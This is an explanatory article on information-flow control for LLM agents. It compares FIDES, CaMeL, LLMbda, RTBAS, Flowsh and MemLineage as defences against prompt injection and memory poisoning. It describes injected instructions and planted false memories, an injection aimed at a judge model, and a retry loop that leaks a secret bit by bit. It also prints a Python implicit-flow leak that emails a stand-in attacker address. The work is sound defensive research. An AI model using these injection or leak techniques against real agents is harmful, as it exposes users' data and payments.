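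This is strong evidence that businesses are trying to plant memories and that doing so takes little skill, but it is weak evidence of harm. Microsoft counted prompts and did not report how many people clicked the buttons, how many memories changed or whether anyone received worse advice. It notes that the effect varied between assistants and over time, and that it could no longer reproduce some previously reported behaviours. Its examples of a business ruined by a biased investment tip and a child exposed to an unsuitable game are hypothetical. MITRE's ATLAS, a public catalogue of attack techniques against AI systems, now includes memory poisoning, which gives security teams a common name for it but no estimate of how often it happens.

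In the laboratory attacks, the injected text arrived in a document, an email or a tool result, all of which a system can mark as untrusted. A "Summarize with AI" link instead puts the company's words in the box where the user types, so a system that labels text by its channel would treat them as the user's own request and mark the resulting memory as trusted. Storing only the user's messages, which worked well against Trojan Hippo, would not keep the advertisement out.

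## What can flow control guarantee within a single task?

The taint rule that Das and colleagues tested stopped every attack, but it also kept the assistant from reading an email and answering it in the same session. Since 2025, several research groups have built agents meant to keep this protection while blocking less legitimate work, and some have proved theorems about what their agents prevent. Most of these designs cover a single session, so the labels only have to last until it ends.

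### What noninterference requires

The precise statement of noninterference compares two runs of the same program. Let the label $n$ stand for an observer who may see every value whose label may flow to $n$. Write $s \sim_n s'$ when two starting states agree on all of those values, whatever else differs between them. A program $P$ that always gives the same output for the same input satisfies noninterference if, for every $n$,

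$$s \sim_n s' \;\Rightarrow\; P(s) \sim_n P(s')$$

Suppose Ana is the observer, and $s$ and $s'$ are two versions of the office memory that differ only in Ben's salary. The reply to Ana must then be the same in both cases, so she can't learn the salary from it however she words her question.

The same formula covers integrity. Here $s$ and $s'$ differ only in the text of the supplier's web page, and $n$ is "trusted". Every result that still has the "trusted" label must be the same in both runs. If the payment tool accepts only trusted account numbers, nothing on the page can change where the money goes. This property covers any text an attacker might write, whereas testing a filter shows only that it catches the attacks in the test.

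### Chance and unfinished runs

A language model can answer the same prompt differently each time, so there is no single $P(s)$ to compare. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) compare probabilities instead. Let $\mu_s(q)$ be the probability that a run starting from $s$ finishes with a result that looks like $q$ to the observer. Exact probabilistic noninterference requires $\mu_s = \mu_{s'}$ whenever $s \sim_n s'$.

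That is too strict for a system that enforces its rules by stopping runs, because the decision to stop may itself depend on a secret. Most proofs in this field therefore establish only a weaker, termination-insensitive property, which lets the secret affect whether a run finishes but nothing else. A run that the system blocks counts as unfinished, so the probabilities $\mu_s(q)$ can sum to less than 1.

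Suppose the assistant chooses at random whether to write Ana a long or a short draft of the budget. If Ben's salary is high, the long draft always triggers a forbidden step and the run stops.

| Ben's salary | Long draft | Short draft | Run stops |
|---|---|---|---|
| Low | 50% | 50% | 0% |
| High | 0% | 50% | 50% |

An obvious approach is to compare only the finished runs. Garby and colleagues tried this and found that it gives the wrong definition. In the example, half of the finished runs produce a long draft when the salary is low and none do when it is high, so the test would report a leak even though the salary affected only whether a run finished. Their definition instead asks for a third distribution $\omega$ that is at least as large as both:

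$$\mu_s(q) \le \omega(q) \;\text{ and }\; \mu_{s'}(q) \le \omega(q) \;\text{ for all } q, \qquad \sum_q \omega(q) \le 1$$

In other words, there must be a way to assign outcomes to the unfinished runs that gives both cases the same distribution. Here an $\omega$ of 50% long and 50% short works. If the draft were long 90% of the time for a low salary and short 90% of the time for a high one, the probabilities in $\omega$ would have to add up to at least 1.8, so the definition would reject the program.

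Garby and colleagues also prove a limit on how far apart the two distributions can be. Half the sum of the differences $|\mu_s(q) - \mu_{s'}(q)|$ is at most the average chance that a run doesn't finish. In the example both numbers are 25%. The guarantee is therefore strong only for an agent that nearly always finishes. It also doesn't cover what Ana can work out from seeing a run stop, which in the example is that Ben's salary is high.

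### FIDES keeps untrusted text away from the planner

In 2023 the programmer Simon Willison proposed the dual-LLM pattern, also called the dual-model pattern, to protect agents from injected instructions. A privileged model plans the work and calls the tools but never reads untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that can't call any tools. An injected instruction may corrupt the quarantined model's answer, but it can't directly cause an action.

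Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, combine this pattern with labels in a planner called FIDES. A planner here is the software that decides what the model sees and passes on its tool calls. Suppose Ana asks the assistant to summarise her three latest emails and send the summary to Ben:

1. Ana's request is trusted, so the context starts with the label "trusted".
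2. The model calls the email tool. FIDES compares the label of each part of the result with the label of the context. It stores any part with a more restrictive label in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name, such as "#read_emails_0". The context stays trusted.
3. The model asks the quarantined model to summarise whatever is in that variable. FIDES puts the summary in a second variable, which inherits the "untrusted" label.
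4. The model calls the messaging tool, with Ben as the recipient and the second variable as the message.
5. FIDES replaces the variable with its contents and checks the call. The choice of tool and recipient came from a trusted context, so the policy can allow the call even though the message itself is untrusted. A separate rule can check that Ben may read everything in the message.

A malicious email can't change who receives the summary, but it can still cause the quarantined model to write an empty or false one. Ben will receive that summary unless the policy also requires the message to be trusted.

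In some tasks, the planner's actions depend on the content of the hidden text, for example "if anyone has asked for a meeting, put it in my calendar". FIDES can show the planner the whole variable, but this makes the context untrusted, so later actions may fail the policy check. It can instead query the quarantined model and restrict the answer to a fixed format, such as yes or no. The label records this format, and a policy may allow an action that depends on one untrusted yes-or-no answer, because an attacker can do much less with one bit than with a paragraph.

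Those bits can add up, however. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) describes a version of FIDES for agents that operate a computer through its screen. Hiding everything on the screen left the planner with no information to act on, so the researchers let it read yes-or-no values. The planner could eventually learn everything in a hidden variable by asking about it repeatedly, so they limited the number of steps to reduce this leak.

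For confidentiality, Costa and colleagues prove explicit secrecy, a weaker property than noninterference. Any sequence of steps the agent performed is treated as a fixed function $g$ of the stored data. Explicit secrecy requires that if two sets of data $d_1$ and $d_2$ agree on everything public, then $g(d_1)$ and $g(d_2)$ do too. This prevents the agent from copying Ben's salary into a public message, but the agent could still send a harmless public message only when the salary is high, because the property doesn't cover what an observer learns from the choice of steps.

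Costa and colleagues chose the weaker property because full noninterference would essentially prevent an agent from writing anything public after reading anything secret. Their proof assumes that the model always gives the same answer to the same prompt.

### CaMeL turns the request into a program

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, also separates a privileged model from a quarantined one. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), the privileged model writes a plan based only on the user's request. The quarantined model processes untrusted data without access to tools. A custom interpreter tracks where each value came from and checks the policies before every tool call.

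The plan is a program. For "pay the supplier's invoice", it might open the invoice, have the quarantined model extract the amount, look up the account number in Ana's own records and call the payment tool. If the invoice contains an instruction to email the payroll file to a stranger, no email is sent, because the program has no step that sends one. The invoice can still change the amount. Separating the two models doesn't prevent this, so the system has to use labels and policies.

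Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) note in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that CaMeL's plan can't depend on what the tools return, whereas FIDES lets the model look inside a variable, though doing so taints the model's context. CaMeL is therefore less flexible when the user doesn't know in advance what the task will involve.

CaMeL's programs are written in a restricted form of Python. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) argues that Python's exceptions and dynamic types make strong guarantees about information flow difficult, and recommends a simpler language designed for security. CaMeL has no theorem comparable to the one for FIDES, and its designers called formalisation a crucial direction for further work.

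### Two leaks in CaMeL's tracking

Both leaks that Garby and colleagues describe are implicit flows, in which the program never copies the secret anywhere. In their example, an agent manages a customer's bank account, and an attacker wants to know whether the balance is above some threshold. The direct attack is to send an email if the balance is high. CaMeL blocks this because it treats everything inside a branch as secret when the branch condition depends on the balance.

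The first leak gets around this with two extra variables. J. S. Fenton described the trick in 1974, and it can be written like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the first branch runs and "tmp" becomes false, with the label "secret". The second branch then doesn't run, so "rich" stays true and keeps its original label, "public". CaMeL therefore treats the last condition as public and allows the email. If the balance is low, "tmp" stays true and public, the second branch sets "rich" to false, and the program sends nothing. In both cases "rich" reveals whether the balance is high, but it is still labeled "public". CaMeL misses the leak because it raises a variable's label only in a branch that runs, even though skipping a branch can also reveal information.

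An attacker would have trouble getting CaMeL to run this program, because the privileged model writes the code without seeing the attacker's text. But this separation can fail. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with its policy checks off, a user's request to follow the instructions in a file led the model to write a small interpreter that could carry out any instructions the file contained. Whoever wrote the file could then choose the agent's actions.

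The second leak comes from the code around the interpreter. If a program fails, an ordinary Python loop, in which CaMeL doesn't track labels, has the privileged model try again. Whether the policy blocks a run can depend on a secret, so each run can reveal one bit. A termination-insensitive guarantee would allow one such bit, but the loop can start new runs that each test a different condition, and twenty runs are enough to pick out one balance from about a million. CaMeL censors the error messages it passes back to the model, which makes the leak harder to exploit but doesn't provide a formal guarantee.

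### LLMbda labels the conversation itself

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for writing agents, to make such gaps impossible. Every value has a label. The conversation with the model also has a label, which is the join of the labels of all the messages the program has sent in it. Anything the model replies gets at least that label, including code it writes and the results of running that code. A model that has read the supplier's page can therefore produce only untrusted values.

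If a program had only one conversation, the whole session would quickly become untrusted. LLMbda has three commands for dealing with this. "Fork" runs part of the program in a temporary copy of the conversation, then discards the copy and restores the original with its old label. "Clear" empties the current conversation. "Endorse" raises the integrity label of a value.

Suppose the assistant has to sort an incoming email as an invoice, a complaint or something else. The program forks the conversation, clears the copy and asks the model to classify the email in that copy. The answer is untrusted, but the main conversation remains trusted because it has never contained the email. The program endorses the answer only after checking that it is one of the permitted categories. With eight categories, the sender can influence the trusted part of the program by at most three bits. A programmer can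 therefore write the dual-model pattern using fork and clear, whereas FIDES and CaMeL build it into the system.

To prevent the first leak, LLMbda stops a run if a branch that depends on a secret tries to add a message to a public conversation. Relabelling the conversation as secret at that point wouldn't be enough, because it would still be public in a run that skipped the branch, just like "rich" in CaMeL. Stopping the run may reveal one bit, which the theorem allows.

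To prevent the second, the retry loop runs inside LLMbda, so labels follow the error messages too. But then one failed attempt that had read untrusted data would taint every later attempt. Garby and colleagues' test agent, Randori, avoids this by testing its program on made-up data, which is safe to trust. It revises the program until it works and only then runs it on the real data.

The main theorem is that every LLMbda program satisfies the probabilistic, termination-insensitive form of noninterference, including programs that the model writes while the agent is running. A second theorem is that endorsing a value, which weakens integrity protection, can't be used to leak secrets, whatever the attacker puts in the untrusted data. Garby and colleagues checked both proofs with Lean, a program that verifies mathematical proofs. The proofs apply to the same interpreter that calls the language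 model, which avoids the risk of proving something about a design and then implementing it incorrectly.

### RTBAS asks the user when labels can't settle the matter

A system can also ask the user before every action, but people soon stop reading the questions. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent that asks only when it can't establish from the labels that an action is safe.

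Before each step, RTBAS uses a screener to estimate which parts of the conversation matter for the agent's next action. The screener can be a second language model or a small neural network that uses attention scores, which indicate how strongly each part of the input affects the output. RTBAS joins the labels of the parts the screener selects and hides everything with a label more restrictive than the joined one. If the policy allows a tool call with the joined label, the call goes ahead. Otherwise, the user decides whether to allow it.

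The screener will sometimes be wrong, but its mistakes should reduce usefulness, not security. If it overlooks an untrusted email, RTBAS hides the email from the model. If it includes an email that doesn't matter, the label becomes stricter and the user may have to answer an unnecessary question.

Zhong and colleagues tested this on 37 tasks involving private data, such as booking a flight with a stored credit card. Asking the user before every tool call led to unnecessary questions in 11 tasks, compared with 3 for RTBAS when a language model did the screening. In 4 tasks, RTBAS should have asked the user but instead hid private data that the user might have wanted it to use.

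### What the checks cost

Researchers have tested all four designs on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office work, travel booking, banking and Slack messaging. It has 97 ordinary tasks, which can be run with or without injected instructions in the data. The scores below are for GPT-4o, now an old model, and show the percentage of tasks that Costa and colleagues' agents completed when there was no attack:

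| Agent | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Basic agent with policy checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES with policy checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

Without checks, 152 attacks succeeded against the basic agent. With checks, none succeeded against either agent, after Costa and colleagues excluded a few that the benchmark had misjudged or that the policies deliberately allowed. Hiding data in variables recovered much of the lost usefulness except in the travel tasks, where the policies already allowed most of the necessary actions and GPT-4o had trouble using the variables. OpenAI's o1 used the variables better and completed 68% of the travel tasks.

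Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, so no attack could arrive through a mislabeled field. The perfect security score therefore shows only that the checks work when the labels are right, as the theory predicts.

Some of the lost tasks were unsafe to begin with. Many banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, and the policy is meant to stop agents from obeying untrusted files. Slack tasks had the same problem in RTBAS's test on AgentDojo. Their completion rate fell to 33% with one screener and 22% with the other, although RTBAS lost no more than about 3% over the whole benchmark under attack. The test had no user to ask, so the agent skipped every call that RTBAS flagged. A user who approved the legitimate calls would have raised the scores.

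Kolluri and colleagues argue that such comparisons are unfair to flow control. In practice, unprotected agents also ask for permission before consequential actions, but the usual scores count tasks they could finish only with unlimited approvals. Using OpenAI's o3-mini, the basic agent completed 24.3% of tasks without any approval, a basic agent with labels 35.5%, and FIDES 50.1%. The researchers' own agent, Prudentia, completed 59.1%. It is built on FIDES but also tells the model about the labels and policies, so the model can plan around them.

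This seems right to me as an account of the cost, though it assumes that users approve legitimate actions and catch malicious ones.

 

That assumption is doubtful. *Flowsh* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) cites an Anthropic report that users approve about 93% of Claude Code's permission requests and pay less attention as the requests pile up. Asking users less often may therefore improve security as well as convenience.

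Garby and colleagues compared Randori with CaMeL on the 16 banking tasks, running each task three times. The table shows the percentage completed when there was no attack:

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Randori, checks on | 75.0 | 64.6 |
| CaMeL, checks off | 66.7 | 70.8 |
| CaMeL, checks on | 37.5 | 37.5 |

Turning on CaMeL's checks roughly halved its score, while Randori did about as well with checks as CaMeL did without them. With so few tasks, the margins of error are around 20 percentage points or more, so the differences between the first two rows mean little. The comparison with the last row is also imperfect, because Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and its programs may endorse untrusted data. Without endorsement, Randori's score with MiMo-v2.5 fell to 54.2%.

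TypeGuard, a system that enforces similar policies through the Haskell programming language, also completes fewer tasks when its policies are enforced. Garby and colleagues cite results in which it completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks without policies and 8 with them, compared with 7 for CaMeL under the same conditions.

For the security test, Garby and colleagues combined each banking task with nine attacks and ran every pair three times on each of three models. Randori resisted the attack in all but two of the 1,296 runs. In about two thirds of the pairs, the attack was easy to resist because it needed a tool that the agent's program would never call. Even against CaMeL without checks, attacks succeeded in only 5 of the 622 runs that finished. The benchmark gives little evidence that Randori is safer in practice, so the case for it rests mainly on the proofs.

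Both successful attacks on Randori involved the same task. The user asks the agent to pay a bill described in a text file, but the attacker has replaced the file with a different payment request. Randori blocked this attack when it couldn't endorse data. With endorsement, it couldn't tell a real bill from a false one, because both come from the same untrusted file. Ana's assistant has the same problem with the supplier's new bank account.

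### What the theorems take for granted

The theorems assume that data has the right label when it enters the agent. In RTBAS's AgentDojo test, one injected instruction was in text the user had supposedly written. The text was labeled "trusted", so RTBAS didn't track it. The "Summarize with AI" links described earlier would exploit the same weakness. Confidentiality labels can be wrong too. Costa and colleagues used an email's sender and recipients to infer who could read it, but acknowledge that somebody may have shared the email more widely.

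*SPA* (2026) points out that some systems replace simple labels with detailed records of origin and permission. These records can express finer rules, but the guarantee then also depends on somebody writing a correct and complete policy for each tool. FIDES, CaMeL and Prudentia all assume that the user, the planning model and the tools are trustworthy, so they don't protect against a malicious tool. They also don't prevent mistakes, such as a model misreading Ana's request and paying the wrong invoice.

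Finally, tracking has to cover every route the data can take. CaMeL's retry loop was one gap, and Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL also treated an untrusted value as trusted once it was inserted into a longer piece of text. LLMbda closes such gaps inside the language, but its proofs treat all data sources as part of the program, whereas a real agent uses outside services and files.

Flow control is especially difficult on the command line, because a single command can start other programs that read files the model never sees. Flowsh, a command-line tool for agents, therefore tracks which files and network connections each command uses while it runs. It checks file changes before applying them and network requests before sending them. Compared with a permissive sandbox that asked for approval of every action it couldn't show to be safe, Flowsh needed 5.8 times fewer approvals per completed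 task on a set of office tasks and 22.5 times fewer on Terminal-Bench, a benchmark of command-line work. It also completed fewer tasks, by 7.9 percentage points on the office tasks and 9.7 on Terminal-Bench.

Zhong and colleagues give an example of a gap between two tools. One tool is allowed to send private messages, and the other returns sent messages with the label "public". An agent can remove a message's private label without breaking any rule by sending the message to itself and reading it back. Persistent memory can lose labels in the same way, even if each session satisfies noninterference by itself. Flowsh stores labels with the files so that a later session can still read the labels.

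## How can labels stay attached to stored memories?

As Costa and colleagues describe it, FIDES attaches labels to the messages, tool results and variables of a single run, all of which disappear when the run ends. On Monday, the system marks the note about the supplier's new bank account as untrusted. On Thursday, the note comes back from memory as plain text with no label, so the system has to assume one. If it assumes "trusted", the false account number passes the payment check. If it assumes "untrusted", everything the assistant has saved becomes untrusted, including Ana's own rule about phoning first, and no session that reads the assistant's memory can make a payment.

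### Storing the label with the file

For an agent that keeps its memory in files, Kim and colleagues' Flowsh stores each file's label in its extended attributes, a small space that Linux provides for information about a file. The label is attached to the file, not its path, and it survives the end of the session and a restart of the computer. When a command changes an existing file, Flowsh joins the command's label with the one already there, so an agent can't make an untrusted file trusted by adding to it. The agent can't edit the label either, because Flowsh replaces any label a command writes with its own. A file that never had a label gets a default, which in the sample configuration is "untrusted" and readable only by the user.

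Two similar tools, Tether and ActPlane, store their labels in the monitor's own data or in the operating system's kernel. According to Kim and colleagues, neither tool's paper explains how file labels carry over to a later session. *ActPlane* (2026) specifies labels that can be added but not removed, so its rules can be checked throughout a session, but a memory attack involves at least two sessions.

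Flowsh gives each file one label for all its contents, which works poorly for memory files. If the assistant keeps its notes in a single file, one line from the supplier's page makes the whole file untrusted, and nothing the assistant writes later can change that. Splitting the notes into many files only partly solves the problem, because file names can also carry information. Flowsh therefore keeps one label for all the names in a directory and treats listing the directory as reading them all. Once a session that has read the web creates a file in the memory directory, any later session that lists the directory becomes untrusted before it opens any notes.

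In a memory system that rewrites its entries, a label written into the text could vanish when the system merges two notes, so the label needs to be stored outside the text. Louck (2026), in *Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning*, ran a monitor on top of one such system, Mem0. The labels survived because the monitor kept them in a separate record instead of trying to recover them from the rewritten text.

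### What else the store has to record

To check whether a memory entry is correctly labeled "trusted" or "untrusted", the system needs to store, along with the label, the entry's origin, the person or program that wrote it, and the earlier entries used to produce it. It also needs some protection against an attacker who changes the label in the database.

*Clawed and Dangerous* (2026) sketches what such an entry could look like. The entry links the stored text to the tool call that produced it, the step in the agent's plan that made the call, and the user's original request. It also includes an expiry date and the permission under which the agent wrote it. If Ana's company found out that Monday's session had read a tampered page, it could use these records to quarantine everything that session saved. The format is an illustration, and nobody has tested it.

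*Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes a working system that does part of this. The software around the model keeps the labels and references to the exact versions of the sources. An item with several sources gets the join of their labels, even if the model appears to have ignored one of the sources. Lowering an item's sensitivity or raising its integrity requires a special permission that the model's memory tools can't request.

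However, Zhang doesn't protect the records cryptographically, so an administrator with direct access to the database could alter them. That may be acceptable on Ana's own computer, but less so when several companies' agents write to one hosted store. Such protection seems to be rare. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 71 works on recording what agents do and found that they rarely reported tamper-evident records.

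### What a signature proves

*Memlineage* (Ouyang and Hou, 2026) combines all these elements in a system of the same name. Each memory entry holds its content, its writer, a trust level, a list of parent entries and a number for how strongly each parent influenced it. It also holds a hash of the original source, a short fingerprint that changes if the source changes.

The writer then signs the whole record with a private key. Anyone with the matching public key can check the signature, but only the holder of the private key can produce it. If an attacker changes "untrusted" to "trusted" in the database, the signature no longer matches, and MemLineage drops the entry when the agent tries to retrieve it. It also drops entries from any writer whose public key isn't in its register.

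Signatures don't reveal that an entry is missing, so MemLineage also keeps an append-only log. It builds a Merkle tree by hashing each entry's identifier and signature, then hashing the results in pairs until only one hash, the root, remains. Changing or removing any old entry would change the root, and proving that an entry belongs to a log of 256 entries takes only eight other hashes. To delete an entry, the system adds a "tombstone" with the entry's identifier and the reason, and leaves the old hash in place. These protections assume that the computer running the agent can be trusted, since it holds both the private keys and the reference copy of the root.

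None of this would have protected Ana, because the assistant summarizes the supplier's page in its own words and signs the summary with its own key. If it summarized Ana's instructions, it would sign that summary the same way. Both signatures would be genuine, since the assistant wrote both summaries, so a system that checks only signatures can't tell them apart. Comparing the summary with the page wouldn't reliably show where it came from either, because the two may have no sentence in common.

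A valid signature does not show that a memory is true. *MutMem* (Saidi, 2026) notes that "A false claim can be correctly signed". MutMem signs changes to memory as well as entries. When later events show that a memory was useful or misleading, the system raises or lowers a value that sets how often it retrieves the memory, and signs the old value, the new value and the memory's identifier together. An attacker who edits the value directly has no valid signature for the change, and a signature copied from another memory fails because it covers the wrong identifier. A signed change took about 5 milliseconds.

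MutMem also signs its judgements about which memories look poisoned. Saidi planted 500 false passages aimed at 100 questions. When the system didn't use the signed judgements, at least one false passage appeared in the top five search results for 94 of the questions. When it used them, no false passage appeared in the top five for any question. The judgements came from a detector that looks for groups of passages with the same unusual opening. The signatures prevent anyone from changing a judgement afterwards, but an attacker might evade the detector by giving each passage a different opening.

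### How taint passes to descendants

To record what an entry came from, MemLineage builds a graph. An edge runs from a parent $p$ to a new entry $c$ if $p$ was in the model's context when the model wrote $c$. Each edge has a weight $w(p,c)$ between 0 and 1, an estimate of how much the parent influenced the new entry. Trust levels run from 0 for trusted entries to 3 for outside content, with 1 and 2 for entries derived from trusted and untrusted material. The level of a new entry is

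$$\text{trust}(c) = \max_{p \in P_c} \; \mathbf{1}[w(p,c) > \tau] \cdot \text{trust}(p)$$

where $P_c$ is the set of parents and $\tau$ is a threshold that the operator chooses. The bracketed term is 1 if the weight is above the threshold and 0 otherwise. The new entry therefore takes the worst level among the parents that influenced it strongly enough.

Suppose the assistant's weekly summary has two parents. Monday's note from the supplier's page has level 3 and weight 0.6, and Ana's rule about phoning has level 0 and weight 0.8. With a threshold of 0.3, both parents count and the summary gets level 3. With a threshold of 0.7, only Ana's rule counts, and the summary gets level 0 even if it contains the false account number. Raising the threshold makes the system more permissive because fewer parents count toward the summary's level.

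If every weight is 1, the rule is the ordinary join for integrity labels. A threshold adds a kind of automatic endorsement, because it lets the system ignore an untrusted parent whose influence seems small. The rule deals only with integrity, so if Ben's salary were a third parent, the summary's level would be the same and the rule would not stop Ana from reading the summary.

Ouyang and Hou prove a theorem they call Untrusted-Path Persistence. It applies to any chain of entries $p_0 \rightarrow p_1 \rightarrow \dots \rightarrow p_k$ in which each entry is a parent of the next. If $p_0$ has level 2 or 3 and every weight along the chain is above $\tau$, then $p_k$ also has level 2 or 3. The proof goes one step at a time. If $p_{k-1}$ is untrusted and the weight of its edge to $p_k$ is above $\tau$, its level is included in the maximum for $p_k$, which is therefore at least 2. Because the signed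 records keep the levels and parents, the chain can span any number of sessions.

The theorem resembles Biba's result about chains of reads and writes, but its conditions are harder to meet because MemLineage has to list the right parents and estimate their influence, while Biba's monitor only had to observe that a process had read an object.

Even the list of parents can be incomplete. By default, MemLineage takes a new entry's parents from the most recent retrieval. If the assistant retrieves Monday's note, then the delivery dates, and then writes its summary, the note may be missing from the summary's parents even though it is still in the context.

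### Where the threshold loses the taint

An attacker's text may pass through several summaries before it causes harm. To study this, Ouyang and Hou assume that the first edge has a weight of 0.9 and that each later weight is 0.7 times the one before:

$$w_k = 0.9 \times 0.7^{\,k-1}$$

The taint survives $K$ steps only if all $K$ weights are above the threshold. Since the weights fall, the last one decides.

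| | 1 step | 2 steps | 3 steps | 4 steps | 5 steps |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Weight of the last edge | 0.9 | 0.63 | 0.441 | 0.309 | 0.216 |
| Threshold 0.10 | kept | kept | kept | kept | kept |
| Threshold 0.30 | kept | kept | kept | kept | lost |
| Threshold 0.50 | kept | kept | lost | lost | lost |
| Threshold 0.90 | lost | lost | lost | lost | lost |

With a threshold of 0.30, the taint's weight is above the threshold by less than 0.01 at the fourth step, and the taint is lost at the fifth. The published results match this arithmetic for one, two, three and five steps but don't include four, so that column comes from the formula alone. The last row is "lost" throughout because the first weight is exactly 0.9 and the rule requires a weight strictly above the threshold.

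For chains of up to five steps, Ouyang and Hou recommend a threshold of 0.10 or lower, although any threshold below 0.216 would work under this formula. A threshold of 0.10 only postpones the problem, because the weight falls to about 0.106 at the seventh step and 0.074 at the eighth. An assistant that writes a weekly summary based on the previous week's would reach the eighth step in two months.

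The weights might not fall this way in practice. Each weight measures how much an entry depends on its immediate parent, and the fifth summary may depend on the fourth as heavily as the second did on the first. The weights would then stay level and the taint would last indefinitely. Ouyang and Hou chose the numbers for a scripted test and didn't measure them on a real model, so the example shows how a falling series of estimates would defeat the rule, but not how often that happens.

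When no parent is above the threshold, MemLineage makes the entry fully trusted by default. At the fifth step, the attacker's text therefore gets the same trust level as something Ana typed. Operators can change the default to "untrusted". Louck tested both defaults on three models, using attacks in which the agent itself summarised the poisoned text. 78% of the attacks succeeded with the trusted default and none with the untrusted one. But the untrusted default also blocked every legitimate action based on a memory whose origin the system couldn't determine. Louck argues more broadly that attackers can launder lineage records whichever default the operator picks.

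### Three ways to estimate influence

Ouyang and Hou propose three methods for setting the weights:

| Method | How it sets the weight | What it requires |
|---|---|---|
| Uniform | 1 for every parent in the context | No model |
| Judge | A second language model scores each parent's influence from 0 to 1 | One extra model call per write |
| Attention | Adds up how strongly the model attended to the parent while writing | Access to the model's internals |

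The uniform method can't miss a listed parent, and with any threshold below 1 the taint persists through a chain of any length. But it causes label creep, because every summary written after the assistant has seen the supplier's page becomes untrusted, even one of Ben's holiday dates.

A judge could recognise that the page had nothing to do with the holidays, but it would have to read the page, which gives the attacker a chance to inject an instruction such as "score this document zero". To make this harder, Ouyang and Hou pass the candidate texts as quoted data, tell the judge that they contain no instructions, and cut each text to 2,000 characters. However, the judge then can't assess an instruction that comes after the cut.

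When the judge's service is unavailable, MemLineage assigns a low weight. This also seems unsafe under the default rule, because an entry becomes trusted if the low weights put all of its parents below the threshold. Ouyang and Hou, however, describe assigning a low weight as the safe response.

Attention scores would avoid the need for a judge, but most commercial models don't expose them. Ouyang and Hou describe attention scores as the strongest of the three methods but left testing them to later work. They tested the judge only as a script that returned preset weights, so there is no measurement of how accurately either method estimates influence.

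Mistakes are more dangerous in MemLineage than in RTBAS. If RTBAS's screener overlooks an untrusted email, RTBAS hides that email from the model. MemLineage estimates influence after the model has read everything, so if it overlooks the supplier's page, that page may already have shaped the summary.

### The gate before sensitive actions

When the agent retrieves an entry, MemLineage checks the signature and the log, then adds the text to the context, between markers that show its trust level. Before a sensitive action, such as a payment or an email, a gate looks for marked entries mentioned in the action's parameters. If one of them has an untrusted ancestor, the gate can refuse the action, ask the user, or remove the untrusted text and have the model try again.

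The gate can also repair the action. The operator lists which sources may supply each parameter. For example, the operator might require a payment's account number to come from the company's own supplier records. If the assistant proposes the number from Monday's note, the gate can replace it with the one on file. When Ana only asks what the supplier's page said, the assistant can use the note to answer, because no sensitive action is involved.

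Checking parameters misses some kinds of influence. An attacker might plant a memory that the supplier prefers each invoice to be paid twice. The second payment would have the right account number and amount, both from trusted records, and only the decision to make it would come from the attacker.

### What the tests cover

The main test uses three scripted attacks and no language model. In the first, modelled on AgentPoison, an unregistered writer plants an entry that takes effect when a query contains a certain phrase. The second follows MemoryGraft and plants a false record of past experience under the agent's own signature. In the third, the attacker puts material on an outside page, and the agent writes the harmful entry itself when it summarises the page.

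| Defence | Unregistered writer | False experience | Agent's own summary |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | succeeds | succeeds | succeeds |
| Signatures and log | blocked | succeeds | succeeds |
| MemLineage | blocked | blocked | blocked |

The results confirm that signatures alone aren't enough and that the code follows its rules. But each cell shows the outcome of one fixed script, so "blocked" doesn't mean that MemLineage would stop every attack of that kind. The test also used uniform weights, so it didn't have to estimate influence.

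Ouyang and Hou then looked for ways around the defence. The attack succeeded when the agent saved a summary without listing its untrusted parent, or when the parent's weight (0.20) was below the threshold (0.30). Stricter settings stopped both attacks. One of these settings refuses any sensitive action based on an entry without parents, which also blocks a legitimate reminder that the user typed directly.

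In a smaller test with real models, the agent summarised an outside document in one session and retrieved the summary in the next. Without a defence, GPT-5.3-Codex carried out the harmful action in 5 of 20 trials, and GPT-5.4-mini did so in 2 of 10. With MemLineage, neither model did. The samples are so small that the true rates with MemLineage could be as high as 16% and 28%, respectively.

The last test used six banking cases from AgentDojo, which combined three user tasks with two attacks. With ordinary settings, only one of the six attacks succeeded against the unprotected agent. Ouyang and Hou therefore set up a deliberately vulnerable agent that treated workflow records in tool results as trusted instructions. All six attacks succeeded against this agent without MemLineage, and none did with it. The vulnerable agent completed the user's task in two of the six cases without protection,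 two when MemLineage refused suspicious payments, and four when MemLineage repaired them.

AgentDojo has no tasks that span sessions, so these cases test the gate but not whether labels persist. The repairs also took the correct bill details from the benchmark's own answers. A real company would have to connect the gate to a trustworthy source of invoices.

MemLineage adds little delay. Writing an entry took 0.21 milliseconds, and checking and labelling eight retrieved entries took 0.72 milliseconds. These figures don't include a judge, which would add a model call to every write. Generating a proof from the log took 0.016 milliseconds with 16 entries and 0.30 milliseconds with 256. If the time kept growing at that rate, it would pass a millisecond before the log reached 1,000 entries. A command took 412 to 982 milliseconds in Flowsh, compared with 61 to 78 milliseconds in a permissive sandbox.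 Flowsh has to find out which files each command opened, while MemLineage gets its list of parents from the agent's software.

### Labels that need no estimate

A store can avoid estimating influence by keeping everything derived from an untrusted source untrusted. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) takes this approach. The system trusts only what the user types and the exact values that somebody has confirmed, and it never alters a stored block. As in FIDES, the main model receives only references to untrusted material, and a quarantined model reads the material itself. A summary by the quarantined model stays untrusted however many times it goes back into memory.

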